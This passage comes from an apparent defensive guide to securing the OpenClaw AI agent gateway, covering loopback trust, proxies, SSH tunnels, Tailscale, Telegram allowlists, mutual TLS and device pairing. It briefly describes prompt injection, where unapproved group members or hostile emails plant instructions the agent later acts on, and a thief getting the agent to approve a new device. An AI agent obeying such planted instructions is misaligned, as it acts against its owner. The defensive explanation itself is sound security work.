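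Chrome closed that gap on 7 April, according to Google's *Chrome 147* (2026). Developers had first tested the change on half of Chrome's beta users. In the discussion of Chromium's *Intent to Ship* (2026), they said Chrome's usage data showed the use of WebSockets to local addresses at about 0.1%, and noted that some of it came from sites checking visitors for fraud.

Firefox 153 turned on the permission for all users on 21 July (Mozilla, *Firefox Release Notes*, 2026). The Firefox 154 beta, released a day later, extended it to WebSockets (Mozilla, *Firefox Beta and Developer Edition Release Notes*, 2026). In July, Gower (2026) was still proposing the basic check for Safari's engine in *Add the Local Network Access check algorithm and a NetworkProcess-resident permission stub*. Someone who manages an agent from a Mac shouldn't assume that Safari will show a permission prompt.

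The permission prompt would have interrupted the ClawJacked attack before the first guess. It would have done less against CVE-2026-25253. The permission covers requests from public sites to local addresses, but in that attack the local control page sent the token to a public server. The prompt would have appeared only when the hostile page tried to use the stolen token on the local gateway.

Chrome 147 also lets a page navigate a whole browser window to a local address. Van Ieperen found that the permission works against traditional DNS rebinding, but that a newer variant exploits this exception. The variant opens a new window, so an attentive user has a better chance of noticing it.

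Users may also grant permission out of habit or without understanding the request. An early version of Chrome's prompt said that the site wanted to look for devices on the local network. Users couldn't tell from this that the site might reach an AI agent with access to a mailbox. Van Ieperen worries that frequent harmless requests will teach people to click "Allow". This may not be a big problem yet, since a crawl of 45,000 popular sites found only 73 attempts at local access, mostly for bot detection, by developers' mistake or to reach a companion app.

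### A proxy makes strangers look local

Branquinho recounted that in late January people on X were discussing OpenClaw control panels that had accidentally become public. A reverse proxy on the gateway's machine can cause this. It forwards visitors' requests over the loopback address, so a gateway that gives local callers special treatment gives it to everyone on the internet.

A proxy can pass on the visitor's real address in a header, usually called `X-Forwarded-For`. But any caller can write that header, so the gateway should accept it only from a proxy the operator has registered. The proxy must also overwrite whatever the visitor sent, so that it passes on only the real address. If a visitor at 203.0.113.7 sends a header containing 127.0.0.1 and the proxy just adds to it, the gateway receives both addresses and will treat the visitor as local if it reads the first one.

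According to OpenClaw's current documentation, operators should list their proxies in the `trustedProxies` setting. If a request with forwarding headers comes from an unlisted address, the gateway doesn't treat it as local. If the unlisted proxy runs on the gateway's own machine, the gateway rejects the request on routes that need its login, even when the token is correct. This is inconvenient for someone setting up a proxy for the first time, but a clear error is better than letting anyone use the control panel.

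The gateway cannot detect a proxy that adds no forwarding headers. The widely used proxy nginx adds them only if the operator configures it to. A visitor who connects through a proxy that omits them still needs the token, but the gateway has no sign that the connection came from another machine.

OpenClaw can also let a proxy handle the login and report who the user is. By default, this mode refuses proxies on the same machine, because any other program there could forge the proxy's headers. OSV's March advisory, *GHSA-5wcw-8jjv-m286* (2026), describes how untrusted websites could bypass the origin check in this mode and gain administrator access. The ClawJacked fix two weeks earlier had deliberately kept connections through trusted proxies working. An operator who adds a proxy therefore needs to test its origin checks separately.

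### Other programs on the machine

Every user account on a computer shares the same loopback address. On a family desktop or a university server, a program run by another person can connect to the gateway even if it can't open the owner's files. Browser permissions don't prevent this, and neither do origin checks, because a program other than a browser can set the origin to any value.

A gateway needs authentication even on loopback. OpenClaw's setup now generates a token by default for local use too, and the gateway refuses WebSocket connections if the operator hasn't configured a valid login method. Malware running under the owner's account can usually read the token from the disk, so the token gives little protection against it. Pasting the token into a local script can also give that script too much access, because anything that uses the token on the gateway's web interface gets full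 operator rights, even if it requests fewer.

OpenClaw still treats local callers more leniently in two ways. First, the gateway slows down repeated wrong password attempts over loopback but never locks the caller out. The developers chose this because a lockout could block the owner's own command-line tool before the gateway had checked its credentials. With a lockout, any program on the machine could shut out the owner by sending enough wrong guesses.

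The delay is a weak defence because the gateway checks the password before it waits. A program that opens a thousand connections can have a thousand guesses checked at once, and the delay only holds back replies to wrong guesses. The developers acknowledge this, and the real protection is a long random token. The gateway limits browser connections more strictly and counts their attempts separately for each website, so a hostile page can't use up the control page's attempts.

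The second exception is automatic pairing. When a program connects directly over loopback with a valid token, the gateway approves its device key without asking the owner. Devices on the home network have to wait for approval, as do programs on the gateway's own machine that connect through the machine's Tailscale address. Automatic pairing doesn't apply if the request carries forwarding headers or comes from a browser client other than the control page.

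Automatically approving local connections is a reasonable convenience on a laptop with one user and no untrusted software. Malware running under that user's account could probably copy the keys of an approved device anyway, so an extra prompt would add little protection. On a shared machine, automatic approval removes the one step that might alert the owner to a stolen token. The developers describe the ability to reach the loopback address as a trust boundary in its own right. Operators who have to run untrusted programs should keep them off the gateway's machine, or in a sandbox that can't connect to the gateway's port.

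## Reaching the agent from elsewhere without a public port

A gateway that accepts only local connections is inconvenient when the owner is away from home and wants to give the agent a task from a phone, see what it did overnight, or answer an approval prompt (a request to confirm an action before the agent carries it out). If the owner's laptop is often asleep, OpenClaw suggests running the gateway on a machine that stays on, such as a home server or a rented server. The owner then uses the laptop only for remote control.

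The owner can reach the agent from elsewhere without changing the bind address by using an SSH tunnel or a private network, which can carry a connection to the gateway's machine and deliver it there over loopback. OpenClaw's *Gateway exposure runbook* ranks these as the narrowest exposure, followed by a proxy that signs users in, with a public address as the widest.

### SSH tunnels

SSH is the standard program for logging in to another computer over an encrypted connection, and it can carry other programs' traffic too. An owner with a laptop would run a command like this:

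`ssh -N -L 18789:127.0.0.1:18789 user@home-server`

SSH then listens on port 18789 of the laptop's loopback address. When the owner opens that address in a browser, SSH encrypts the request and sends it to the SSH server on the gateway's machine. The server connects to port 18789 on that machine, so the request reaches the gateway from 127.0.0.1, as if the browser were running there.

The SSH server first checks the user's identity, usually with a key stored on the laptop, and the gateway then requires its own token. The user doesn't have to trust any other company, because the internet provider carries only encrypted traffic. But the laptop must be able to reach the SSH server. Rented servers usually have SSH open already, while a home machine needs a forwarded port on the router or a private network. Opening a port for SSH is still safer than opening one for the gateway, since SSH has had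 decades of scrutiny and OpenClaw already has a long list of known vulnerabilities.

A thief with the unlocked laptop may gain access to more than the agent, because an ordinary SSH key opens a command line on the gateway's machine, where the thief can read `openclaw.json` and the transcripts. The operator can protect the key with a passphrase and restrict it to forwarding connections to port 18789.

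The tunnel also creates the loopback problem on a second machine. While the tunnel is open, any program on the laptop or web page in its browser can try to connect to the gateway, which treats all these connections as local.

### Private overlay networks

SSH tunnels don't suit phones well, and OpenClaw's phone apps can't set one up. An overlay network is easier. It links chosen devices over the internet as if they were on one private network.

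Tailscale, the service OpenClaw supports directly, calls each of these networks a tailnet. Every device has its own key pair. Tailscale runs a coordination server that gives each device the others' public keys and addresses, along with rules about who may connect to what. The devices then encrypt the traffic between them. They set this up through outgoing connections, so the home router needs no forwarding rule.

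OpenClaw's *Give your Gateway a stable HTTPS URL* uses Tailscale Serve, and the gateway keeps listening on 127.0.0.1. The owner's phone opens an address ending in `.ts.net` and connects through the owner's private Tailscale network to port 443 on the gateway's machine. The Tailscale program there decrypts the request and passes it to the gateway over loopback.

Tailscale also removes any login name the caller put in the request and adds the user's actual login name. OpenClaw's *Tailscale* explains that the gateway confirms this name with the Tailscale program on its own machine. When the gateway uses the usual token login, this check replaces the token for the control page by default. It also lets a browser skip the usual pairing step if it presents a device key, which browsers can generate themselves. So by default, anyone permitted to connect to port 443 can operate the agent.

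That permission can be wider than the owner intends. The example rule in OpenClaw's instructions admits every member of the tailnet. Tailscale notes that requests from outsiders who have accepted a share of the machine also carry login names. Someone who shared a home server with a friend to stream films may therefore also have given that friend access to the agent's control page. An owner can prevent this by naming only their own devices in the tailnet's rules and setting `gateway.auth.allowTailscale` to `false`, which makes the gateway require its token again.

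The owner also has to trust Tailscale and the account they sign in with. A compromised coordination server could add an attacker's device to the network. Tailscale's *Tailnet Lock* describes an optional defence that requires trusted devices to sign each new device before it can send or receive traffic.

A stolen phone that is still enrolled in the tailnet can reach whatever the tailnet's rules allow, often including services unrelated to the agent. If the phone can open the control page, the thief can ask the agent to run commands, and OpenClaw runs them without approval by default. The owner can remove the phone from the tailnet using another device, without logging in to the gateway's machine.

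An overlay network may also let the gateway's machine connect to other devices on the owner's tailnet, such as a laptop or file server, and the agent can use the same route. *Giving AI agents access to private systems*, from Enclave, a company with a product similar to Tailscale, recommends giving an unattended agent its own machine and network identity. If the agent runs on an administrator's workstation instead, network rules can't distinguish its traffic from the administrator's.

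### Serve and Funnel: private and public sharing

Tailscale has a second feature, Funnel, that publishes a local service to the whole internet. In Tailscale's examples, `tailscale serve 3000` and `tailscale funnel 3000` produce the same web address, and the main difference in the output is in the first line, which has "within your tailnet" for Serve and "on the internet" for Funnel. Serve and Funnel can't share a port, so whether the port is private or public depends on which command was run last.

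A visitor to a Funnel address first reaches one of Tailscale's relay servers, which forwards the encrypted connection to the owner's machine. According to Tailscale, the relay can't decrypt the traffic and hides the machine's internet address. This protects the owner's privacy but doesn't stop strangers from reaching the gateway. They can find its web address because certificate authorities publish the names on the certificates they issue.

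Public visitors through Funnel arrive without a Tailscale login name, so OpenClaw won't start its own Funnel mode unless the operator has set a password. Scanning the home's public address won't reveal a Funnel, because visitors connect to the relay instead. The operator should run `tailscale funnel status` and check whether the tailnet's rules allow Funnel. Tailscale's documentation is inconsistent about whether Funnel is on by default.

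Tailscale's *Funnel vs. sharing devices* describes device sharing as an option for a single guest. It admits one named person, so access is much narrower than with Funnel, but a guest who can operate the gateway can do anything the agent can.

### Identity-aware proxies

An identity-aware proxy lets staff reach an agent with their normal work login, without installing anything. It is a server that signs users in before forwarding their requests. The browser connects to the proxy, which sends the user to the company's login service and checks that they have permission. The proxy then adds the user's name to the request and forwards it to the gateway. The gateway accepts the name only from the proxy's address and can check it against its own list, `allowUsers`.

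OpenClaw treats an empty `allowUsers` list as permission for everyone the proxy has signed in, so a proxy that accepts any Google account could let in almost anyone. The gateway must also be reachable only through the proxy, or a caller could bypass it and supply a false name. OpenClaw's security audit always reports this mode as a critical finding, even in a correct setup, to remind the operator that security depends on the proxy.

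The operator has to trust the proxy, which can read the decrypted traffic, and the login service, whose administrators can create or reset accounts. But the proxy can limit what a user does, for example by passing on a request with read-only rights, whereas the gateway's shared token always gives full control.

A thief with a signed-in laptop can use the agent until the session expires or an administrator ends it. In a tutorial on putting the Pomerium proxy in front of OpenClaw, iximiuz Labs gives the authorised user administrator rights over the gateway and advises readers to treat that identity as "a privileged credential". For one person, OpenClaw recommends Tailscale Serve instead because it is simpler to set up.

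### A public address

With a forwarded port and no proxy, a browser connects directly to the gateway, and the gateway's login is the only barrier. Without HTTPS, anyone who can watch the traffic can copy the login token. If a laptop holding the token is stolen, the owner has to change the token, because removing the laptop from a network doesn't cancel it.

OpenClaw advises against this arrangement. An operator who needs a public address should make an identity-aware proxy the only route to the gateway, limit repeated login attempts and run other people's sessions in a sandbox.

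Some vendors provide remote access through their own accounts. OpenAI's *Remote connections* requires a phone and a Mac to be signed in to the same ChatGPT account and workspace before the phone can control the Codex agent on the Mac. The user doesn't have to configure a network, but anyone who takes over the account may also be able to reach the Mac.

### Chat channels as a second entrance

Many owners never open the control page remotely, because they can message the agent on Telegram. This works with the port closed because the gateway uses long polling. It sends Telegram a request for new messages, and Telegram holds the request open until a message arrives or the request times out. The gateway handles the reply and sends another request.

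The alternative to polling is a webhook, a web address to which the chat service sends each message. The address has to be public, so a gateway on a private network can't use one on its own. OpenClaw's *Telegram transports* describes polling as the default and webhooks as an option. Telegram includes a secret in each webhook request instead of the gateway's token, and the gateway rejects requests that lack the secret. An operator who needs a webhook can publish only its path, such as `/telegram-webhook`, and keep the control page private.

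The choice of connection depends partly on the service. *Understanding Communication Model Choices Through OpenClaw's Integration Approaches*, by the blogger stefaniezhao77, lists Slack as supporting both webhooks and a persistent connection called Socket Mode, and Discord as using a WebSocket. The gateway can open these persistent connections itself, so it needs no public address for them.

Kunpeng's *Disable Public Network Access, Bind to Local Address*, from Huawei's server-chip business, warns that Feishu, WeChat, WeCom and WhatsApp stop working when public access is off. This warning is too broad for WhatsApp. WhatsApp's official business interface pushes messages to a public address, but OpenClaw normally links to WhatsApp as an extra device, much as WhatsApp's web version does. That connection is outgoing, so it doesn't need a public port.

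The agent relies on Telegram to identify who sent a message, so anyone who takes over an approved Telegram account can instruct the agent from anywhere, even with the port closed.

### Choosing who can message the agent

OpenClaw has four settings for direct messages. The default is pairing, in which the owner approves a code for each new sender. With an allowlist (a list of permitted senders), strangers get no code. The open setting accepts everyone, and the disabled setting accepts nobody.

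The eight-character codes expire after an hour, and OpenClaw's *Access control and allowlists* gives a limit of three pending requests per channel. The limit prevents a flood of requests, but three strangers could fill it and delay someone the owner wants to admit. A code doesn't prove who the requester is, so if a message claiming to come from a colleague asks the owner to approve one, the owner should check with the colleague some other way.

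The owner should pair first because, according to OpenClaw's *Telegram access control*, the first person approved becomes the command owner if the gateway doesn't have one yet. That person can use owner-only commands and answer approval prompts. For an agent with one user, OpenClaw recommends an allowlist containing that person's numeric Telegram ID. A username is a worse identifier because someone else can take it if its holder gives it up.

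Approval for direct messages doesn't carry over to groups. By default, OpenClaw ignores every Telegram group until the operator lists it. In a listed group, the gateway also checks the sender against an allowlist and normally requires a mention of the agent's name. The mention rule prevents accidental replies but does little against a hostile member, who can type the name.

Group members who can't trigger the agent may still influence it. When an approved person mentions the agent, the gateway by default also gives the model recent group messages and any quoted text, including text from people who aren't on the allowlist. One of them could post an instruction and wait for an approved person to trigger the agent. Setting `contextVisibility` to `"allowlist"` filters out text from people who aren't on the allowlist.

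An attacker with limited access to the gateway may be able to change the allowlist. An advisory in the OSV database describes a flaw that let a client without administrator rights do this by sending an `/allowlist` command as a chat message, even though the gateway blocked the same client from editing the settings directly. After any break-in, the owner should therefore check the allowlists for unfamiliar senders.

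### Why approving a sender does not isolate them

By default, everyone's direct messages go into one shared session. If an owner and a flatmate both message the agent, the model may answer the flatmate using something the owner said earlier. Setting `session.dmScope` to `"per-channel-peer"` gives each sender a separate conversation on each channel.

Separate conversations still share the agent's tools and credentials, so if the flatmate asks for the latest email from the owner's bank, the gateway can search the mailbox for it. OpenClaw describes the session label as a way to route messages, and the label does not grant or deny permissions.

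The sandbox mode `non-main` restricts every session except the main one. If the operator leaves direct messages in the shared session, which is the main one, an approved friend's requests run outside the sandbox. This mode restricts the friend only if the operator keeps direct messages in separate sessions.

The gateway can also block certain tools for certain senders. OpenClaw's Telegram example blocks the file-writing and file-editing tools for everyone except one user ID. Senders who can run shell commands could still change files, so the operator should block command execution too. These limits are useful among people who trust each other, but anyone outside that group still needs a separate gateway.

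### A home machine used from a phone

Suppose one person runs OpenClaw on a computer at home and wants to use it from a phone, both through the OpenClaw app and through Telegram. The main settings would be:

```json5
{
  gateway: {
    bind: "loopback",
    tailscale: { mode: "serve" },
    auth: {
      mode: "token",
      token: "<long random token>",
      allowTailscale: false,
    },
  },
  channels: {
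    telegram: {
      dmPolicy: "allowlist",
      allowFrom: ["<owner's numeric ID>"],
    },
  },
}
```

The owner installs Tailscale on the phone and the computer, and writes a rule that lets the phone connect to port 443 on the computer. New tailnets usually start with a rule that lets every device connect to every other, so the owner has to remove that rule. The app connects to the computer's `.ts.net` address, and the owner approves the app's device key, as the next section explains. The agent polls Telegram for messages, so the router doesn't need to forward any ports.

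The owner should then test that unauthorized people cannot reach the agent. With Tailscale switched off on the phone, the `.ts.net` address should not load. A message from a friend's Telegram account should get no reply. On the computer, the earlier `lsof` or `ss` check should show port 18789 only on a loopback address.

These ways in remain:

| Way in | What an attacker needs | What reduces the risk |
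| --- | --- | --- |
| Telegram | The owner's account or unlocked phone | A screen lock and Telegram's two-step password |
| The gateway, through the tailnet | The phone with its saved login, or the token and another device the rules admit | A screen lock and a rule that names only the phone |
| A new device on the tailnet | The owner's Tailscale sign-in or control of Tailscale's server, and then the gateway's token | Tailnet Lock and a strong sign-in |
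| Accidental publication | A `tailscale funnel` command on the computer, which the agent itself may be able to run | Removing permission for Funnel from the tailnet's rules |
| The home computer | Physical access, a remote-login password, or malicious software such as a bad skill | Turning off unused remote login and installing little else |
| A web page in the computer's browser | A flaw in the gateway's origin checks | Updates, and browsing on another machine |
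| Text the agent reads | An email or web page with hostile instructions, and no connection to the gateway | Limits on the agent's tools, accounts and outbound connections |

The phone is the weakest point because it holds both ways of reaching the agent. If approval prompts also go to Telegram, a thief can request an action and then approve it. NVIDIA's *What Is the Best Tool for Monitoring and Controlling a Sandboxed AI* describes a partial separation in NemoClaw, where the owner chats with the agent through Telegram but approves blocked network requests in a terminal program. This protects against a stolen phone, but the owner can't approve those requests from Telegram when away from a terminal.

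An owner who loses the phone needs another device to remove the phone from the tailnet and end its Telegram session. It makes sense to set up that device in advance, or at least to have someone at home who can switch the computer off. Once back at the computer, the owner should disable the Telegram channel, change the gateway's token and the passwords of any accounts the agent could use, and check the logs before turning remote access back on.

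## Proving identity with certificates and device keys

A bearer token works for anyone who copies it, and copies of OpenClaw's gateway token end up in browsers, scripts and backups as well as in `openclaw.json`. The January flaw in the control page was serious because the gateway accepts a stolen token as if the owner had sent it.

A device can instead prove that it holds a secret without sending it. Client certificates and OpenClaw's device pairing both work this way. iximiuz Labs' *Secure Machine-to-Machine Access with mTLS and Pomerium* cautions that someone who steals the secret from the device can still impersonate the device. But attackers have far fewer opportunities to steal a secret that never leaves the device.

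### Key pairs, signatures and certificates

The device generates a private key, which it keeps, and a matching public key, which it can give to anyone. It uses the private key to compute a signature for a message. Anyone with the public key can check that the signature fits the message, but can't use either the key or the signature to sign a different message. If a server sends a fresh random number and the device returns a valid signature for it, the device must have the private key. An eavesdropper who records the signature can't reuse it, because the next connection will use a different number.

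The server must also be able to identify the public key's owner. A certificate is a signed statement that binds a name to a public key, and its signer is called a certificate authority. Browsers come with a list of public authorities, which check that a website's operator controls its domain name.

An operator can also create a private certificate authority, which is another key pair with its own certificate, and set the server to accept only client certificates signed by that authority. A stranger can make a certificate with the name "phone" on it, but can't add the authority's signature.

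### A mutual TLS connection, step by step

TLS is the encryption used by HTTPS. It usually authenticates only the server, as Aleinikov (2026), in *mTLS vs TLS*, explains, while mutual TLS authenticates the client too. Suppose a laptop connects to a server at `agent.example.com` using TLS 1.3, the current version:

1. The laptop and the server exchange random values and temporary public keys. Both sides use these to compute the same encryption keys, and they encrypt everything that follows.
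2. The server asks for a client certificate and sends its own certificate. It then signs a digest of all the messages so far.
3. The laptop checks that the server's certificate contains the name `agent.example.com`, hasn't expired and comes from an authority the laptop trusts. It uses the public key in the certificate to check the server's signature. If any check fails, the laptop disconnects.
4. The laptop sends its own certificate and signs a digest of the handshake, which now includes the server's certificate.
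5. The server checks the laptop's signature, the dates on its certificate and the private authority's signature on it. If the operator has supplied a list of cancelled certificates, the server checks that too.

Signing the whole handshake protects against an impostor who relays messages between the laptop and the server. The impostor has to carry out a separate handshake with each. The laptop's signature is valid only for the laptop's handshake with the impostor, so the server rejects it.

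A stranger without a certificate fails at step 5. Some servers drop the connection, while the web server nginx returns an error page. In iximiuz Labs' setup, the proxy Pomerium answered such a request with error 495. If a separate proxy checks certificates, the gateway never receives the stranger's request, so the stranger can't exploit a bug in the gateway's login code.

The proxy's TLS code can also have bugs. In 2014 the Heartbleed flaw in OpenSSL, a widely used TLS library, let strangers read parts of a server's memory without logging in. Still, OpenSSL and SSH have both had far more scrutiny than OpenClaw.

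### Issuing certificates, then losing a phone

Suppose an owner creates a private certificate authority on 1 March and issues two client certificates, one to a laptop and one to a phone, each valid for 90 days. Ideally, each device generates its own private key and sends only the public key to the authority for signing, so no copy of the private key exists elsewhere.

The owner can get the server's certificate from a public certificate authority. Otherwise, the owner has to set the phone to trust a private authority, and anyone who stole that authority's key might be able to impersonate other websites to the phone.

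On 10 April the owner loses the phone. If the owner does nothing, a thief who can unlock it can connect until the certificate expires on 30 May. Cisco AI Defense's *mTLS the gateway* recommends replacing client certificates every 90 days, but its sample commands create certificates that last 365 days. With one of those, the thief could connect for 325 days after the loss. Replacing a certificate doesn't cancel the old one, so a certificate's lifetime has to match the replacement schedule.

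The owner can block the phone sooner by revoking its certificate. The private authority signs a revocation list containing the certificate's serial number, and the owner gives this list to the proxy. The laptop keeps working because it has its own certificate. If the two devices shared one, the owner would have to replace it on the laptop too. Cisco AI Defense also warns that people who share a certificate can't be told apart in the logs.

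A new revocation list takes effect only when nginx reloads its configuration or restarts. A reload leaves existing connections open, and OpenClaw's WebSocket connections can last for hours, so disconnecting the thief requires a full restart. The list also expires, after which nginx refuses every client certificate until the owner signs a new list.

The alternative is to list the certificates that may connect. iximiuz Labs' Pomerium setup identifies the permitted certificate by its fingerprint, a short digest of its contents. In the tutorial, changing the fingerprint in the policy makes Pomerium refuse the same client without a restart, even though the client's certificate is still valid. For someone with two or three devices, listing the permitted certificates is simpler than using a revocation list.

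The owner has to update a fingerprint list whenever a device gets a new certificate. To avoid locking the device out, the owner can allow both the old and new fingerprints, test the new certificate, and then remove the old fingerprint.

The certificate authority's signing key needs the most protection. Anyone who steals it can issue new certificates under any name, and the owner can't revoke certificates they don't know about. iximiuz Labs recommends keeping the key in a hardware security module, which signs without releasing it, or in a tightly controlled secrets service.

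At home, an encrypted USB drive in a drawer is a reasonable substitute. The signing key should never be on the gateway's machine, where an agent running outside a sandbox could read it. A list of accepted certificate fingerprints limits the damage if the key is stolen, because any new certificates the thief signs won't be on the list.

### A proxy that checks certificates

Many programs can't check client certificates, so operators usually put a proxy in front of them. Cisco AI Defense describes this arrangement for DefenseClaw, Cisco's security software for agents. DefenseClaw's control interface stays on the loopback address, while nginx accepts outside connections and requires a certificate.

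Adapted for OpenClaw, the nginx configuration could look like this:

```nginx
server {
  listen 9443 ssl;
  server_name agent.example.com;

  ssl_certificate        /etc/agent-tls/server.crt;
  ssl_certificate_key    /etc/agent-tls/server.key;
  ssl_client_certificate /etc/agent-tls/client-ca.crt;
  ssl_verify_client      on;
  ssl_crl                /etc/agent-tls/revoked.crl;

  location / {
    proxy_set_header Connection "upgrade";
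    proxy_set_header Upgrade $http_upgrade;
    proxy_set_header X-Forwarded-For $remote_addr;
    proxy_http_version 1.1;
    proxy_pass http://127.0.0.1:18789;
  }
}
```

The line `ssl_verify_client on` makes the certificate mandatory. The `Upgrade` and `Connection` lines let WebSockets through, and the last header replaces any address the visitor supplied. In OpenClaw's settings, the operator keeps `bind` on `"loopback"`, lists `127.0.0.1` under `trustedProxies` and adds `https://agent.example.com:9443` to the control page's allowed origins.

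The nginx proxy has to be the only way to reach the gateway from the network, because the gateway doesn't check certificates. If the gateway also listens on the home network, or a forgotten Tailscale Funnel leads to it, callers can bypass the proxy. The operator can test this from a device without a certificate. Port 9443 should return an error, and port 18789 should be unreachable.

The device's encrypted connection also has to end at the proxy that checks certificates. Some companies put a load balancer in front of the proxy, which decrypts traffic and opens a new connection to the proxy. iximiuz Labs explains that the proxy then receives the load balancer's certificate or none. The load balancer can avoid this by passing the traffic through without decrypting it.

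Even with a certificate check, the gateway should still require its token, because programs on its own machine can connect over loopback without going through nginx. Browsers can also attach a client certificate to requests from another site's page, so a hostile page open on the laptop might get past nginx with the owner's certificate. The gateway's origin check and token would then have to block the request.

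Client certificates may be awkward to use on phones and with command-line tools. OpenClaw's *Configuration* lists a token, a password and the server's fingerprint among the settings for connecting to a remote gateway, but no client certificate, so OpenClaw's own apps may fail at a proxy that requires one. A browser can usually present an installed certificate.

On a laptop, a helper program such as Ghostunnel can present the certificate for services that can't use TLS themselves. Pogorelec (2026), in *Ghostunnel*, describes it as a proxy that adds mutual authentication and can load renewed certificates without restarting. Like an SSH tunnel, though, it opens a port on the laptop that other local programs can use.

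A proxy with client certificates probably isn't worth the effort for one person who already uses Tailscale, because Tailscale gives each device its own key. It makes more sense for a company that already issues certificates to its machines, or for devices that can't join a private network.

### OpenClaw's gateway doesn't request client certificates

Descriptions of OpenClaw can make it seem that its gateway supports mutual TLS without a proxy. OpenClaw's documentation describes the setting `gateway.tls.caPath` as a file of certificate authorities "for client verification or custom trust chains". *Network Security*, a set of third-party notes on OpenClaw, lists it as an optional path for mutual TLS.

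The code doesn't support this. OpenClaw's gateway runs on Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside a browser. The lesson *Require client authentication* gives the three options a Node.js server needs: `requestCert` to ask for a certificate, `rejectUnauthorized` to refuse an invalid one, and `ca` to name the trusted authority. According to the Node.js project, `requestCert: true` makes the server ask.

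OpenClaw's TLS setup code passes Node.js the server's certificate and key, the file from `caPath` and a minimum TLS version of 1.3. It doesn't set `requestCert`, which is off by default, so the gateway never requests client certificates, even though `caPath` gives it an authority for checking them.

An operator who filled in `caPath` and then opened the port could easily believe that strangers needed a certificate. They would in fact need only to get past the gateway's ordinary login. With TLS turned on, this command tests it from the gateway's machine:

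`curl -k https://127.0.0.1:18789/`

The command presents no client certificate, and `-k` makes it accept the gateway's self-signed certificate. If the gateway returns the control page, it isn't enforcing mutual TLS. The test is worth repeating after updates in case the developers add support.

### How OpenClaw pairs a device

OpenClaw uses keys, not certificates, to identify devices. Each device generates an Ed25519 key pair. According to *Ed25519 Device Authentication*, the device's ID is the SHA-256 hash of its public key. A hash is a short digest that anyone can recompute, and finding a different key with the same hash isn't feasible. A device therefore can't claim another device's ID while using its own key.

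When a device connects, the gateway sends a challenge containing a random value and the time. According to OpenClaw's documentation, the device replies with its ID and public key, the random value, a signature, the login token and the permissions it is requesting. The gateway checks that the ID matches the key, that the signature is valid and that the random value is the one it just sent. It also rejects signatures with a timestamp too far from the current time.

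A valid signature from an unknown device only creates a request for approval. Once the owner approves it, the gateway issues a device token limited to the approved role and permissions, as OpenClaw's *Gateway protocol auth* explains. The device can use this token for later logins, but it must still sign a new challenge each time, and a thief who copied only the token would lack the key needed to sign it.

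Device tokens let the owner cut off one device without changing everyone else's login. In the lost-phone example, the owner would revoke the phone's device token and remove its pairing. If the phone also held the gateway's shared token, the owner should change that too.

A phone that pairs through OpenClaw's setup code gets an operator token that has no administrator rights or permission to change pairings, so a thief can't use the token directly to approve another device or cancel the laptop's access.

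Besides the loopback exception, the gateway by default automatically approves certain new nodes (devices whose functions the agent can use) over SSH. It logs in to the new device's machine and approves the device if the key there matches exactly. This is a good check, but the owner may not see a request for every device. To approve everything by hand, the owner has to set `autoApproveLocal` and `sshVerify` to `false` and leave `autoApproveCidrs`, a list of automatically approved addresses, empty.

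### How device keys differ from client certificates

Both methods rely on a signature from a private key. They differ in who vouches for the key, when the check happens and what the signature covers.

| | Client certificate checked by a proxy | OpenClaw device key |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Who vouches for the key | A private authority, which signs a certificate in advance | The owner or an automatic rule, which approves the key on the gateway |
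| Where the check happens | In the proxy, before the gateway receives anything | In the gateway's own code, after the connection opens |
| What the signature covers | The TLS handshake, including the server's certificate | The gateway's challenge and details such as the device, role and requested permissions |
| How access ends | The certificate expires, or the owner revokes it | The owner revokes the device token or removes the pairing |
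| Permissions included | None, unless the proxy or gateway adds them | The role and permissions the owner approved |

Device pairing is easier to run because there is no signing key to protect and no revocation list to renew. But anyone who can reach the port can send data to the gateway before proving who they are. The gateway has to read that data to check the signature, and a flaw in that code could let a stranger in without a key. Using device keys therefore doesn't justify exposing port 18789 to the internet.

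OpenClaw's signature also gives weaker protection against an impostor between the phone and the gateway. Its documented fields don't identify the encrypted connection or the gateway's certificate, so an impostor could obtain a challenge from the real gateway, pass it to the phone and send the phone's signature back. To prevent this, the phone has to check that it is connected to the real gateway.

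### Pinning the server's certificate

With certificate pinning, a device can check a server without relying on a certificate authority. The device stores the fingerprint of the server's certificate in advance and refuses any server whose certificate has a different fingerprint. In OpenClaw, the owner can enter the fingerprint under `gateway.remote.tlsFingerprint`.

Pinning suits OpenClaw because the gateway can generate its own certificate, which no public authority has signed. This certificate lasts ten years. The owner can get its fingerprint by running this on the gateway's machine:

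`openssl x509 -noout -fingerprint -sha256 -in ~/.openclaw/gateway/tls/gateway-cert.pem`

*Network Security* notes that the gateway also broadcasts its fingerprint over the local network for pinning. Someone else on that network could broadcast a different one, so the owner should copy the fingerprint from the gateway's machine instead.

The Mac app can automatically save a certificate's fingerprint on the first connection, but only if the certificate passes the Mac's normal trust checks. It won't automatically save the fingerprint of the gateway's self-signed certificate or an impostor's.

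If the gateway rejects the shared token, an OpenClaw client may try again with its stored device token, but only over loopback or an encrypted connection with a pinned certificate. Without this restriction, an impostor gateway could reject the shared token to collect the device token.

A device that pins the server's certificate can't connect after the server gets a new one until someone updates the fingerprint. If an nginx proxy sits in front of the server, the device has to pin the proxy's certificate, and certificates from public authorities last only a few months. In that setup, it is easier to check the server's name and the certificate's issuing authority in the usual way.

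### Identity and permission are separate

A valid certificate establishes which device is calling, but someone still has to decide what that device may do. iximiuz Labs demonstrated this with two client certificates from the same private authority. Pomerium allowed the request from the permitted certificate. It accepted the other certificate as genuine but refused the request with error 403, because its policy didn't include that certificate's fingerprint.

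The nginx configuration above has no such policy. It accepts every unrevoked certificate from the private authority, so if the owner issues one to a friend for another service, the friend can also reach the gateway's login page.

OpenClaw attaches permissions to each paired device. A connection may be allowed to read conversations, send requests, answer approval prompts, manage pairings or administer the whole gateway. In version 2026.3.31, the developers further separated identity from permission. Before then, approving a device also exposed the commands it offered, such as taking a picture. According to OpenClaw's *Gateway-owned pairing (Option B)*, those commands now stay off until the owner gives a second approval.

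A team can define roles for people as well as devices. A guest role might let people send requests but require every session they start to run in a sandbox. When an administrator changes someone's role, the gateway immediately disconnects that person, so they have to reconnect with the new permissions.

Permissions on a connection don't necessarily limit what the agent can do. A thief can't use a stolen phone that lacks administrator rights to approve a new device directly, but can still use it to send the agent requests. If the agent runs commands outside a sandbox, the thief could ask it to approve the device from the gateway's own command line.

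### What the Trail of Bits review found

The gateway can identify a caller correctly and assign the right permissions, but lose track of them later. Trail of Bits, a security company, found this problem repeatedly in its 2026 review of OpenClaw.

The review was part of a programme that OpenAI supports, in which engineers use AI models to look for flaws in widely used free software. Trail of Bits' *Introducing Patch the Planet* (2026) reports hundreds of bugs across 19 projects in the first week. OpenAI's *Patch the Planet* explains that such searches also produce false alarms, so security engineers check the findings before passing them to a project.

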